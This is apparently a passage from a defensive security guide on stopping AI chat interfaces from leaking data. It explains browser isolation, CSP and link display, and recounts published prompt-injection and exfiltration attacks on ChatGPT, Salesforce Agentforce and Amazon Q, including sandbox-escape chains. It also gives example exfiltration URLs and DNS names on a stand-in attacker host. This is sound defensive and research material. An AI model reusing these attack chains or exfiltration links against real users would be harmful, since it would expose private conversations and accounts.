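According to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, Noma reported the vulnerability on 28 July 2025 and Salesforce acknowledged the report on 31 July. Salesforce began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents' output on 8 September, and Noma published its findings on 25 September. Salesforce also regained control of the expired domain, according to The Hacker News' *Salesforce patches critical ForcedLeak* (2025).

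Addresses are checked against the new list before they reach the browser, so the check can cover links as well as images. Someone still has to keep the list of names current. Escaping raw HTML would have stopped the published version of the attack, which relied on an HTML image tag.

Other applications can prevent the same mistake with two routine checks. A script can read the hosts from the live policy every day and confirm that each domain is still registered to the expected owner. Developers can also find hosts that are no longer needed by sending a second, report-only policy that omits the suspect host. If no reports arrive over a few weeks of normal use, they can delete the host from the real policy. This would probably have caught an abandoned domain, because a page that still used it would have been showing broken images.

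### What the policy leaves open

No directive in the current draft controls ordinary navigation, such as following a link. `form-action` covers only forms, and an earlier proposal, `navigate-to`, is not in the draft. If a user clicks the false bank link, the browser therefore opens it and sends any private data in its address. Code running in the page can do the same without a click by changing the page's address, and `connect-src` doesn't prevent this. An HTML `meta` element can also send the browser to a new address automatically, so a sanitiser has to remove it even when the page has a strict policy.

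**DNS prefetching.** Before a browser can contact a host, it looks up the host's name in the domain name system (DNS). A page can request this lookup in advance with a `link` element. If the name is `4731.collector.example`, the lookup reaches the name server for `collector.example`, which the attacker runs. The attacker then has the door code, 4731, even though the browser hasn't requested any file. A name can be up to 253 characters long, so one lookup could carry a short sentence.

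The policy draft has rules for prefetching files and for preconnecting, which opens a connection early, but they don't cover a DNS lookup on its own. Browsers have not always followed these rules. According to an old Mozilla bug report, Firefox did not then check preconnect requests against any content policy, and a subdomain can carry information. Markdown can't produce a `link` element, so escaping raw HTML closes this channel, as does a sanitiser with a short allowlist.

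**WebRTC.** Browsers use WebRTC for video calls and other direct connections between computers. A script can give it the address of any server, and `connect-src` doesn't stop the browser from contacting that server. The CSP draft has a directive for this, `webrtc 'block'`, but no browser supported it as of mid-2026, according to CentralCSP, a reference site on these policies. *Add support for the CSP "webrtc" CSP* (Berjon, 2023), which requests it for Safari, had no fix in early 2025, and Mozilla's *Implement CSP 'webrtc' directive* has nobody assigned to it. Browsers ignore directives they don't recognise, so adding this one now does no harm, and it will take effect if support arrives.

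WebRTC matters less than the other two for a chat page, since an attacker has to run code in the page to use it, but it matters a great deal for an application that runs code written by a model.

### Connection allowlists

Google's Mike West, who also helped to write the CSP standard, has drafted a separate mechanism to close these gaps. West, in *Connection Allowlists*, argues that sorting requests by type is the wrong approach to exfiltration, because a leak through a font is as bad as a leak through an image. His proposal has a single list for every kind of connection:

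```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://images.assistant.example/*")
```

The word `response-origin` stands for the page's own origin. The browser refuses any other connection, whether it comes from an image, a script, a name lookup or a video call. Under the draft, the browser also blocks every redirect, even to a permitted address, though West expects developers to need something more flexible.

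Chrome has supported the header since version 152, released on 25 August 2026 (Chrome for Developers, *Chrome 152*, 2026). Coverage grew during the preceding trial. In March, Chromium's *Intent to Experiment* (2026) listed files, navigation, redirects and DNS prefetching as covered from the start, with WebRTC and WebSockets to follow. Report URI's *Connection Allowlist* includes a WebRTC demonstration for Chrome 152. By June no other browser engine had signalled support, according to CentralCSP's *Connection-Allowlist*, so the gaps remain for users of Firefox and Safari. A site needs both headers because the new one limits only where data goes and does not stop injected code from running.

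Control over navigation is the largest gain and also the main obstacle for a chat page. With the header above, the browser would refuse to open the false bank link, but also the genuine sources that an assistant cites. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) suggests a better fit in pages that run generated or untrusted code, which rarely needs to send the user to another page.

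The new list matches names, as CSP does, so it has the same trouble with relays and expired domains. West points out that it also applies to one page rather than the whole origin, so code in a restricted page might open a second page from the same site, one with no list, and send data from there. He recommends putting the restricted content in a sandboxed frame, where it no longer shares an origin with any other page.

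## Isolating HTML that has to run

Some products deliberately run code from a model's reply. ChatGPT can turn a block of HTML into a working page inside the conversation, which OpenAI now calls an HTML preview. Claude has a similar feature called artifacts. A user can ask for a mortgage calculator and then try different interest rates without asking the model again. Markdown can't provide this because it has no sliders, buttons or programs.

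Other companies can supply such pages too. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting models to outside tools and data. Its MCP Apps extension, launched on 26 January 2026, lets a tool return an interactive page. The project gives the example of a database tool that returns hundreds of rows (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The model can summarise them, but a user who wants to sort by revenue or see only last week's sales has to write a new prompt each time. An interactive table lets the user do either with a click.

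A sanitiser no longer helps when the HTML has to run, since it would remove the code that makes the page work. That code may be hostile, either because the model followed a prompt injection while writing it or because the outside company is dishonest. The application has to let the code run while keeping it away from the conversation, the user's account and the network.

Even perfect isolation does not stop attackers from deceiving users. The Decoder's *Attackers abuse shared ChatGPT and Claude chats to spread malware* describes how attackers used ChatGPT's code rendering to build a full fake error page inside a shared chat, with instructions to download an infected desktop app. Victims arrived through paid search ads, and security tools did not flag the link because it was on ChatGPT's own domain.

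Charts often don't need isolation. The model can return numbers and pick a chart type from a list, and the application's own code can draw the chart. Users get less variety, but no code from the reply runs.

### The sandboxed frame and its permissions

An `iframe` element embeds one page in another. If the element has an empty `sandbox` attribute, the browser runs no scripts in the embedded page and blocks its forms, popups and downloads. It also gives the page an opaque origin, which matches no other origin, so the page can't read anything that belongs to the site around it. The developer then gives back individual rights by naming them in the attribute:

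| Permission | What it gives back | Advice for a page the model wrote |
|---|---|---|
| `allow-scripts` | JavaScript | Grant |
| `allow-same-origin` | The page's real origin, with its storage | Grant only on a host set aside for this page |
| `allow-forms` | Form submission | Grant only if the page's own policy has `form-action 'none'` |
| `allow-popups` | New windows and tabs | Withhold |
| `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` | New windows without the frame's restrictions | Withhold |
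| `allow-top-navigation` | Sending the whole tab to another address | Withhold, because the new page could be a fake login |
| `allow-downloads` | Saving files | Withhold |
| `allow-modals` | Dialog boxes | Withhold |

A frame inside a sandboxed frame inherits its restrictions and can't have a permission that the outer frame lacks.

The most dangerous combination is `allow-scripts` with `allow-same-origin` on a framed page from the application's own origin. The framed page's code can then access the surrounding page, remove the `sandbox` attribute from its own frame and reload itself without restrictions.

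Suppose the user of the mailbox assistant asks for an interactive calendar of deliveries. The application can load it like this:

```html
<iframe id="calendar"
        sandbox="allow-scripts"
        src="https://preview.assistant-content.example/7f3a"></iframe>
```

The calendar comes from a separate domain, `assistant-content.example`, even though the sandbox already gives it an opaque origin. The `sandbox` attribute applies only inside the frame, so if someone opens the calendar's address directly in a tab, the code runs with the full rights of the site that served it. The separate domain has nothing for that code to steal. A subdomain of `assistant.example` would be less safe because browsers send some cookies to every subdomain of a site.

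The sandbox stops the calendar from reading the mailbox, but it does not stop the calendar from sending out data it already holds. The model wrote the page after reading the user's mail, and planted instructions could have made it include the door code. The page therefore needs its own content security policy, which its server sends in the header:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  sandbox allow-scripts;
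  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'unsafe-inline';
  style-src 'unsafe-inline';
  img-src data:;
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none';
```

The first line repeats the sandbox, so it also applies if someone opens the page in a tab. The policy includes `'unsafe-inline'` because the inline code here is supposed to run, though it would be a mistake on the chat page. The rest of the policy prevents the calendar from loading or contacting anything, so the model has to put everything the page needs into the HTML, including any charting library.

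The policy still allows WebRTC and navigation, so the calendar's code could navigate its own frame to an outside URL that ends with the door code. The chat page's `frame-src` should list only the preview host, and developers should check that each browser they support then blocks the frame from navigating elsewhere. In Chrome, a connection allowlist can restrict both WebRTC and navigation.

### Messages between frames

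The calendar may need to tell the chat page how tall it is. Browsers provide a function called `postMessage` for this, which works between pages of different origins. Goyal (2026), in *Do the Math*, compares it to a mail slot, through which a page can drop a message into a building it can't enter. Any frame can send a message to the main page, so the code that receives it has to check who sent it and what it contains:

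```js
const calendar = document.getElementById("calendar");

window.addEventListener("message", (event) => {
  if (event.source !== calendar.contentWindow) return;
  if (event.data?.type !== "resize") return;

  const height = Number(event.data.height);
  if (height >= 100 && height <= 800) {
    calendar.style.height = `${height}px`;
  }
});
```

The first check compares windows. Developers usually compare `event.origin` with an expected address instead, but `event.origin` is the string `null` for every frame with an opaque origin, so that check can't distinguish the calendar from another sandboxed page. When the frame has a real origin, the listener should check both the window and the origin.

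A message from the expected sender can still be hostile, because an attacker may have written the calendar's code. The listener above therefore accepts only a number within limits. If it accepted HTML and inserted it into the chat page, the calendar could escape its sandbox through the application's own code. Requests to open a link, post in the chat or use a tool need similar limits, and often the user's approval.

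When an application sends a message to the frame, it normally names the origin that may receive it. An opaque origin can't be named, so the application has to allow any recipient. If the frame has since navigated to another site, that site receives the message.

### Why ChatGPT and Claude use two frames

Barthelet (2026), in *Why MCP and ChatGPT Apps Use Double Iframes*, found that ChatGPT and Claude both put each third-party app in a frame inside another frame. He explains this design by going through simpler designs.

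The host (the chat application) already has the app's HTML, so it could write that HTML straight into a frame's `srcdoc` attribute. Without a sandbox, a `srcdoc` page inherits the origin and content security policy of the page that created it. ChatGPT's policy requires a nonce for inline scripts, so the app's scripts would not run. If OpenAI relaxed the policy, the scripts would run as part of ChatGPT and could read its local storage.

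Sandboxing the frame without `allow-same-origin` fixes that, but the app then has no local storage or cookies, because browsers store these by origin. A shopping app, for example, couldn't use them to save the basket. Adding `allow-same-origin` restores the app's real origin, which for a `srcdoc` page is ChatGPT's.

Each developer could instead serve its app from its own server. OpenAI would then have to keep adding developers' domains to ChatGPT's `frame-src` list as new apps appeared. OpenAI could also serve all the apps from a domain it controls, but that means running a service that delivers other people's code, which smaller companies may not be able to afford.

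With two frames, the host only has to serve one small, unchanging page called a loader:

```
assistant.example                               the conversation
  outer frame: app123.assistant-content.example   the loader
    inner frame: srcdoc                             the app's HTML
```

The host sends the app's HTML to the loader in a message, and the loader writes it into the inner frame. The inner page inherits the loader's origin, so the app can use storage without having the host's origin. Giving each app its own subdomain keeps one app from reading another's local storage. Cookies can be shared across subdomains, so they must be handled separately. According to Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS*, Claude derives the subdomain from a hash of the address of the app's server, so apps from the same server can share an origin.

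In this design the app has the same origin as the loader, so it can change the loader. The outer frame is the real boundary, and the app's policy has to cover both the loader and the inner page. If the policy covered only the inner page, the app could use the loader's functions to make requests the policy forbids.

A2UI, another system for showing interfaces in agent applications, also nests two frames but omits `allow-same-origin` from the inner one. This prevents the app from accessing the loader, but also from using browser storage. It is the better choice for a calendar or chart that doesn't need to save data.

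### How MCP Apps sets the policy

The specification for MCP Apps, which Salomon, Yosef and colleagues (2025), in *SEP-1865*, proposed and which became stable in January 2026, requires the two-frame design for any host that is a web page. The app's developer declares the outside domains that the app needs, in four lists, and the host turns them into a content security policy:

| List | Directives it sets | If the developer leaves it out |
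|---|---|---|
| `connectDomains` | `connect-src` | No outside connections |
| `resourceDomains` | `img-src`, `script-src`, `style-src`, `font-src`, `media-src` | No outside files |
| `frameDomains` | `frame-src` | No embedded pages |
| `baseUriDomains` | `base-uri` | The app's own origin only |

The host may be stricter than the lists but must not allow a domain that is missing from them. Barthelet has seen apps fail in production, or fail OpenAI's review, because their developers forgot to declare a domain. ChatGPT's developer mode at one point stopped enforcing the policy, so the mistake did not show up in testing.

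The lists protect an honest developer's app from injected code, but they do little against a dishonest developer, who can declare their own server. The specification recommends that hosts warn users when an app needs outside domains, and it allows hosts to block domains altogether. Grouping scripts with images and fonts is also a little too permissive, because a developer who declares a domain to load fonts from it also allows scripts from it.

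When an app declares nothing, the specification's stated default forbids all connections, but its sample code for building the policy allows connections to the frame's own origin. The extra permission is harmless as long as the loader's host serves only fixed files. Neither policy includes `form-action`, so a form can send a password to an outside server unless the host leaves `allow-forms` out of the sandbox.

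An MCP App must declare its HTML in advance, separately from the data it will show, so the host can inspect the page, record its hash and refuse a version it doesn't recognise. A page that a model writes during a chat is new every time, so nobody can review it beforehand. Reviewing an MCP App's HTML does not cover scripts that the page later loads from a declared domain.

Apps communicate with the host through `postMessage` in a fixed format that the host can log and check. An app can call tools on its own server, including, by default, every tool the model can call there. The host can ask the user to approve these calls, but the specification does not require it. An app can also add text to the model's context without showing it to the user. A hostile app could use this for prompt injection, so the host should label the text as coming from the app, not the user.

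Salomon and colleagues list misleading content as a remaining risk and ask hosts to show clearly where an app begins and ends. Their specification also lets an app request a display with no border, or one that fills the screen. The host decides whether to grant the request, and a permanent border with the app's name has little downside.

### Parameter: a message that the main page trusted

In October 2026 the security company Parameter used a shared conversation to take over ChatGPT accounts. The victim only had to open the link while signed in. Mukul Goyal's account of the work begins with the question of what code in the HTML preview could still communicate with if it could not enter the main page.

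ChatGPT ran the preview in a restricted frame on a different web address, so the browser blocked Goyal's code when it tried to read the main page. But the conversation also contained an interactive graph, and to draw it ChatGPT had loaded a library called MathLive into the main page. MathLive has an on-screen keyboard for typing formulas and listens for messages about it. In ChatGPT, it accepted those messages from any sender.

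```
chatgpt.com                      main page, with MathLive's listener
  preview frame                  separate origin, sends two messages
  MathLive's keyboard            built from the HTML in the first message
    new frame, no sandbox        origin chatgpt.com, runs the attacker's code
```

The preview sent two messages. One replaced the keyboard's layout, which could contain HTML, and the other made MathLive show the keyboard. MathLive then assigned the attacker's HTML to `innerHTML` in the main page. Before that, the helper function `createHTML` marked the string as trusted without cleaning it, like the Trusted Types policy that returns its input unchanged.

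A script element would not have run there, so the researchers inserted a frame with its own HTML in the `srcdoc` attribute. The frame had no `sandbox` attribute, so the browser gave it the origin of the main page that created it, `chatgpt.com`.

ChatGPT's content security policy still blocked inline scripts in the new frame, but it allowed scripts from YouTube. A YouTube service that supplies information about videos could return its answer as JavaScript, starting with a function name chosen by the requester. The service rejected invalid names, but its error message was also JavaScript and contained the rejected text. The researchers sent their code in place of the name, and the browser ran the error message as a permitted script.

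In the attack described in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026), the code ran with the signed-in user's rights. It could list the victim's conversations, read one that the victim had never shared, and act on the account through ChatGPT's internal interfaces. It sent the stolen text out through an image URL.

Parameter needed several attempts to turn this into a practical attack. The first version required the victim to connect an app that the researchers controlled. In the second, an attached HTML file sent the messages, but sharing the conversation removed the graph, so MathLive never loaded and nothing received them. The version that worked had a graph and a preview written by the assistant in the same conversation, and both remained after sharing. At first the victim had to click the Preview button, but the researchers then marked the HTML so that ChatGPT opened it automatically.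 This worked three times out of three in a separate account, about four and a half seconds after the page opened.

According to Infobae's *Un fallo de ChatGPT permitía acceder a conversaciones privadas* (2026), Parameter reported the flaw on 18 October. OpenAI reproduced it, raised its severity from P2 to P1 on 21 October, and blocked the attack on 26 October, two days before Parameter published. OpenAI paid the researchers $5,000, which Willison thought a bit low for such a serious flaw. Parameter tested only on its own accounts and found no evidence that anyone else had used the attack. On 31 October MathLive released version 0.111.2, whose keyboard accepts messages only from its own origin unless a developer permits others.

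The sandbox kept the preview from reading the main page or running code in it directly. Instead, the preview sent a message that led the main page's own code to insert a keyboard layout containing HTML. MathLive's new default closes that route, but cleaning the layout before inserting it, keeping HTML out of the layout, or removing YouTube from the list of script hosts would also have broken the published attack chain. ChatGPT's use of nonces did not help, because a browser accepts a script that has the right nonce or comes from a listed host. Adding `'strict-dynamic'` would have made the browser ignore the list of hosts.

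An ordinary review of the preview or the graph would not have found the flaw. MathLive's *Mathfield Changelog* shows that its developers added a check on the sending window to the message code in April 2026, but they did so to fix an infinite loop. In June they fixed a separate XSS flaw in how the library displayed text inside formulas. If an application gives a library like this its own sandboxed frame, both kinds of flaw stay inside that frame.

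### Check Point: a permission that undid the sandbox

A week after Parameter's report, the security company Check Point described a different flaw in the same preview. The flaw got around Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting for people who handle sensitive information. OpenAI introduced the setting for organisations and extended it to personal accounts on 4 June 2026.

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* lists what Lockdown Mode limits or turns off: live web access, images in replies, Deep Research, Agent Mode, live connectors to other services, file downloads, and network access for pages made in Canvas, the forerunner of the preview. OpenAI explains on its help page that the setting tries to stop the last step of an attack, when data leaves, and does not keep prompt injections out of the material ChatGPT reads. Willison (2026) approved of the design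 because the limits are fixed rules that don't depend on a model's judgement, though he took the setting's existence to mean that ChatGPT's defaults are not robust against a determined attacker.

The preview already ran in nested sandboxed frames and could not read ChatGPT's cookies or storage, and ChatGPT asked the user before letting it contact an outside server. Popups were the remaining gap. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that ChatGPT intercepted the preview's attempts to open a window, but the sandbox still allowed popups and let them escape its restrictions.

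ChatGPT enforced its block by changing the JavaScript function that opens windows. Every frame has its own copy of that function, and ChatGPT had changed only the copy in the preview's main page. Alexey Bukhteyev of Check Point put another frame inside the page and opened the window from there:

```
preview page       window-opening function replaced by ChatGPT
  child frame      original function, still working
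    popup          outside the sandbox, free to contact any server
```

A stricter `frame-src` would not have prevented this, because a page can create a blank frame, or one with its HTML in `srcdoc`, without loading anything.

An attacker could start from a malicious prompt, a shared chat or a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that anyone can configure and publish. Clubic's *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations* explains that chatting with the attacker's GPT was enough for the popup to send out the victim's messages. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* mentions the victim's entire chat history in its headline, but the published description doesn't support that. The preview could not read the account, so the attacker could get only what the model had written into the page. Parameter's attack,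 by contrast, could fetch old conversations.

Check Point also used the popup to display a fake ChatGPT update with the application's real icon and a link to malware, which the victim still had to click. If the user was signed out, the attack could send the main window to a fake login page.

In an ordinary browser, a page can usually open a popup only after the user clicks or types something. OpenAI built its older desktop application, ChatGPT Classic, with Electron, a tool for turning websites into desktop programs. The application's built-in browser let pages open windows without any user action. The messages were sent without a click, and nothing appeared on the screen.

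OpenAI removed both popup permissions on 18 September 2026, and Check Point confirmed that its method no longer worked. The Hacker News published the details on 5 November. OpenAI will close ChatGPT Classic on 30 January 2027.

Restricting the sandbox's permissions works better than adding code to the preview to disable a feature, because the browser enforces the permissions on every frame inside the sandbox, including frames that hostile code creates later. The added code shares the page with the attacker's code and can miss a copy of whatever it tries to disable. If users need to follow links from a preview, the preview can send the address to the chat page, which can show it to the user before opening it.

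### Testing the frame from the inside

A developer can test the isolation with a harmless page that tries to break out and displays what happened:

| What the test page tries | Expected result |
|---|---|
| Read `parent.document` | An error |
| Open a window from the page itself | No window |
| Open a window from a child frame | No window |
| Send the whole tab to another address | The tab stays |
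| Send its own frame to an outside address | No request |
| Load an image from an outside host | No request |
| Send the main page every message that its libraries accept | No change |

ChatGPT would have passed the first test in both cases. Opening a window from a child frame would have revealed Check Point's flaw. Sending messages to the libraries would have revealed Parameter's, but only if the conversation also contained a graph.

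That condition makes the last test the most work. Chat pages often load libraries only when a reply needs them, so the test conversation should include a formula, a graph, a diagram and anything else the product can display. In Chrome's developer console, `getEventListeners(window).message` lists the functions in the main page that receive messages. Each function, including any that came with a library, needs to check the sender. The developer should repeat the tests in every desktop and phone version, because the embedded browser may follow different rules, as it did in ChatGPT Classic.

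## Showing where a link leads

A content security policy can't stop a user from following a link, so the false bank link in the mailbox reply gets past nearly every defence described so far. Links are harder to do without than remote images, because an assistant that searches the web needs them to show its sources. A link in a reply may take the user to a deceptive site, and clicking it may send out private data contained in its address.

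```
danger       wording              address
deception    bank.example         https://collector.example/
leak         Track your parcel    https://collector.example/track?d=4731
```

The false bank link does no harm until the user types a password, so a user who notices the wrong address can still close the tab.

Clicking the tracking link is enough to leak the door code, because the request contains it. The attacker's server can then redirect the user to the courier's real tracking page, so the user sees the page they expected and suspects nothing.

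In December 2023, Rehberger found that Amazon Q for Business, an assistant for company data, could be made to show a link that read "Sign In" but had a summary of the user's messages in its address. Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business* explains that the instructions to show this link were in a text file that Amazon Q read.

### The parts of an address

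This address names the bank twice and still leads to the attacker:

```
https://bank.example@login.collector.example/bank.example/terms?d=4731

scheme       https
user part    bank.example
host         login.collector.example
path         /bank.example/terms
query        d=4731
```

Only the host determines which server the browser contacts. The host belongs to whoever registered its registrable domain, here `collector.example`. The registrable domain is often the last two parts of the host, but `shop.co.uk` has three parts because a shop can't register `co.uk` itself. Programs look up endings like `co.uk` in the Public Suffix List, which browsers also use.

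Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020), in *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, measured how well each disguise works. They showed 94 people in the United States up to 19 addresses each and asked which website each one belonged to. An answer counted as correct if it gave the domain or its owner, or said that the address was fake. The examples below follow the same patterns as theirs:

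| Disguise | Example | Correct answers |
|---|---|---|
| None | `https://bank.example/` | 93.0% |
| Misspelling | `https://bannk.example/` | 69.8% |
| Lookalike character | `https://bаnk.example/`, with a Cyrillic "а" | 52.7% |
| Bank's name in the path | `https://collector.example/bank.example` | 39.8% |
| Bank's name in the query | `https://collector.example/?bank.example` | 37.2% |
| Reassuring word in the domain | `https://secure-bank.example/` | 36.2% |
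| Bank's name in the user part | `https://bank.example@collector.example/` | 32.1% |
| Bank's name as a subdomain | `https://bank.example.collector.example/` | 31.1% |
| Long chain of subdomains | `https://bank.example.session-83b1-login.collector.example/` | 25.8% |

A correctly spelled name in the wrong part of the URL fooled more people than misspellings and foreign letters, which get much of the attention in security advice. The scheme can also mislead people. Reynolds and colleagues asked participants how they decide whether a link is safe, and the most common answer, given by 29%, was to look for `https`, which any attacker's site can have.

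Software can expose lookalike characters. Before contacting a host whose name contains non-ASCII letters, the browser converts the name to an ASCII form called Punycode, and JavaScript's `URL` class returns that form. An application that prints `url.hostname` will show the fake bank as `xn--bnk-6cd.example`, but it will also show the legitimate `münchen.example` as `xn--mnchen-3ya.example`, which is hard to read. Browsers avoid this by showing Punycode mainly for names that mix alphabets.

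A larger survey shows how hard subdomains are to read. Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020), in *What is this URL's Destination?*, showed 1,929 people 23 addresses each and asked where each would lead. Twelve of the addresses contained a company's name, six in the domain, as in `profile.facebook.com`, and six in the subdomain, as in `facebook.profile.com`. On average, participants answered 5.2 of the six correctly when the name was in the domain, but only 1.2 when it was in the subdomain. 8.3% of participants got all twelve right.

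Experience helped a little, with the heaviest users of technology answering 25.4% of the subdomain questions correctly, compared with 15.9% for the group with the least coding experience. When asked where `facebook.com@google.com` leads, 28.3% chose Facebook and 14.7% chose Google, the correct answer. The survey recruited people through websites for paid online tasks, whose users tend to know more about technology than average, so the general public would probably do worse. Albakry and colleagues point out that looking for a familiar name is a reasonable habit, because nearly every address people see contains only one such name and leads to that site.

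### Wrapped links and the Bing loophole

A user who reads a link's host correctly may still not learn where the link leads. Li (2020) describes how Facebook, Twitter, Microsoft and Google have rewritten links for over a decade so that a click goes first to the company's own server, which then redirects the user. This lets the company count clicks and block dangerous destinations, but the address the user sees names only the redirecting server's host.

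Short links also hide the destination, but people seem to know this. Participants in the survey by Albakry and colleagues gave short links a median safety score of 2 out of 5. They gave the addresses with subdomains a 4, although they misread nearly half of them.

In November 2025, Tenable's *HackedGPT* showed how a wrapper could defeat an automatic check. ChatGPT's `url_safe` service checks links as well as images and leaves out those it considers unsafe, but it approved everything on `bing.com`. Bing sends clicks on its search results through tracking addresses that begin with `bing.com/ck/a` and redirect to the site. Every site in Bing's index therefore has a `bing.com` address that leads to it, which Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) calls "an open redirect as a service".

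Tenable's researchers got their own test sites indexed and copied the tracking addresses. They then left a comment with hidden instructions under a blog post. When a user asked ChatGPT to summarise the post, the summary ended with a link that passed the check and led to the researchers' site. The demonstration worked with GPT-4o and GPT-5.

ChatGPT used a separate model, which Tenable calls SearchGPT, to read web pages. SearchGPT could not see the user's memories or earlier messages, which made leaks harder but did nothing against deceptive links, because it could write one without private data. To steal data, the researchers had to make SearchGPT's answer contain further instructions, which ChatGPT followed when the user sent another message. They hid the instructions on the opening line of a code block, where ChatGPT's page displayed only the first word. A tracking address can't be altered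 to hold data, so they used a separate indexed page for each letter, as in other attacks with fixed addresses.

Tenable reported the loophole in December 2024 and was still asking OpenAI for an update the following March. Embrace The Red dates a stronger version of `url_safe` to around August 2025. The Hacker News reported in November that OpenAI had fixed some of Tenable's seven findings, but did not specify which.

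An application should not automatically follow a wrapped link to find out where it leads, because the request would send any private data in the address before the user clicks. Some wrappers include the destination as a parameter, which the application can read without contacting anyone. For other wrappers, it can only tell the user that the link redirects.

### ChatGPhish and links without a source

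In Permiso's ChatGPhish demonstrations, a summarised page added a false account notice to ChatGPT's answer. The link was labelled "Click here" and led to an unrelated domain whose address was not disguised. The user was meant to trust the link because it appeared in ChatGPT's own reply, in the same formatting as the genuine summary.

Permiso attributes the problem to ChatGPT displaying links from the summarised page as its own, without labelling their source. In a second version, the link appeared under "Additional Resources", a heading that many legitimate summaries might have. Permiso also compares the attack with email phishing. A company can filter incoming mail, wrap its links and train staff to distrust strange messages, but none of this applies to a web page that a user chooses to open and summarise.

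An application can reliably label links that came from the page, because it can search the page's text for the exact address. It can't do the same for sentences, because the model rewrites them. A note such as "link from the page you summarised" would have contradicted the claim that the notice came from ChatGPT. An address that appears nowhere in the material the model read deserves more suspicion, because the model put it together.

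### Ways to display a link

Suppose the attacker combines both dangers and gives the bank link an address that ends in the door code. The application could display it in any of these ways:

```
wording only            bank.example
full address            bank.example (https://collector.example/?d=4731)
domain                  bank.example (collector.example)
address as plain text   https://collector.example/?d=4731, not clickable
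confirmation page       "This link leads to collector.example. Open it?"
no link                 bank.example [link removed]
```

| Design | Deceptive site | Private data in the address | Cost in harmless replies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wording only | User must check the browser's preview | Leaks on a click | None |
| Full address | User can notice the host | User can notice a readable code, but not an encoded one | Clutter |
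| Domain | Easiest for the user to notice | Hidden from the user | A few extra words |
| Address as plain text | User must copy it to reach the site | Leaks only if the user copies and opens it | Copying every source by hand |
| Confirmation page | User gets a second chance | Can show the data, if the application detects it | An extra click |
| No link | Stopped | Stopped | No sources to open |

When a link shows only its text, users have to hover over it to see its address in the browser. They can't hover on a phone, and fewer people know how to check a link there. In the study by Reynolds and colleagues, 62% of participants said it was "very true" that they could check a link's target on a computer, compared with 34% on a phone or tablet.

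The full address gives users the most information, but they don't read all of it. Ramkumar et al. (2020) tracked people's eyes as they judged addresses and found that longer addresses got more attention only up to a point. Participants relied mainly on the part that contains the host. Checking the host helps users spot deceptive sites, but private data is usually further along, in the path or query.

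The domain alone is easier to read, but it doesn't always show whose page it is. Albakry and colleagues mention `googleusercontent.com`, which Google owns but which hosts its customers' pages, so an attacker's page there would appear under a Google domain. If each customer has a separate subdomain, showing the whole host, with the registrable domain in bold, at least lets readers see which customer's page it is.

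If the host is too long for the screen, the application should shorten it at the start. Style rules usually cut text at the end, which removes the part that identifies the owner:

```
whole host          bank.example.session-83b1-login.collector.example
cut at the end      bank.example.session-83b1...
cut at the start    ...83b1-login.collector.example
```

The application also has to generate the label itself, from the parsed address, and give it an appearance that markdown can't produce. Otherwise the model could write "(bank.example)" after the link as ordinary text, and users would take it for the label. The application can also compare the real host with the link's text and flag a mismatch, such as a link that reads `bank.example` but leads to `collector.example`. It should only compare text that has a real domain ending, or it would flag a link called "Node.js".

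Preview cards that show a page's title or picture bring back the automatic request, as Slack's link previews do. Even a card that shows only the site's icon can leak the door code if the code is in a subdomain.

**Removing links.** Amazon fixed the sign-in link problem by replacing addresses in replies with the text "[URL not displayed]". It deployed the fix worldwide on 29 December 2023, 25 days after the report, and Rehberger described it publicly in January 2024. He noted that Microsoft 365 Chat also removed addresses at the time, with a message saying it did so for privacy reasons. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Willison took a similar view that April, advising developers whose models read untrusted text to be careful with images "or even outbound links".

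Removing links is quick to deploy and doesn't depend on the user, but it has to cover every form of link. In EchoLeak, a reference-style link got past Microsoft's filter. After removing the model's links, an application can safely restore links to its sources by having the model write only a source number, which the application replaces with the address it recorded when it retrieved the document. The model can't add private data to that address, although the document may still be an attacker's page.

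**Asking for confirmation.** ChatGPT can ask the user to confirm a link when OpenAI's crawler has not already recorded its address. According to OpenAI, the dialog is headed "Check this link is safe", shows the address and lets the user copy or open it. OpenAI says a related check that shows the user the data about to be sent also covers page visits and bookmarks in its Atlas browser.

The dialog deals with leaks, and OpenAI says the rule behind it doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or won't try to manipulate the user. An attacker can get a phishing page past the rule by publishing it and waiting for the crawler to record it.

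Asking users to confirm every link would be tiresome, and they would soon click through without reading. Ouyang and Narechania (2026), in *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References in LLM-powered Conversational AI*, counted an average of 9.5 references per ChatGPT answer. *URL Inspection Tasks* (2025) tries to prevent careless clicking in email by making the user solve a small puzzle about the address before the page opens. That might be reasonable for a rare and suspicious link, but not for ten sources in one answer.

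### Where a warning works best

Petelka, Zou and Schaub (2019), in *Put Your Warning Where Your Link Is*, tested the position of warnings with 701 people. Participants opened ten emails, supposedly to report whether the links worked, and three of the emails contained a phishing link. Each group saw one type of warning or none:

| Warning | Phishing links clicked |
|---|---|
| None | 77% |
| Banner above the email | 44% |
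| Beside the link, always visible | 34% |
| Beside the link, on hovering | 30% |
| Beside the link, always visible, with the original link disabled | 16% |
| Full page in the browser after the click | 12% |
| Beside the link, on hovering, with the original link disabled | 9% |

Disabling the original link, so that participants could continue only by clicking the real domain inside the warning, made a large difference. Whether the warning appeared on hovering or was there from the start hardly mattered. Participants clicked harmless links about equally often in every group, so the warnings did not simply put them off clicking links. The results may overstate how well the full-page warning works, because participants who saw it had already learned what they needed to report about the link.

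A chat application can use the idea without an extra click by leaving the wording as plain text and making the domain next to it the link. It is unlikely to get the same results, because the warnings in the experiment read "Fake Website, Don't Click!" and appeared only on links that the researchers knew to be bad. A neutral domain label on every link is a much weaker signal, and Petelka and colleagues did not test one.

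### Whether displaying addresses is worthwhile

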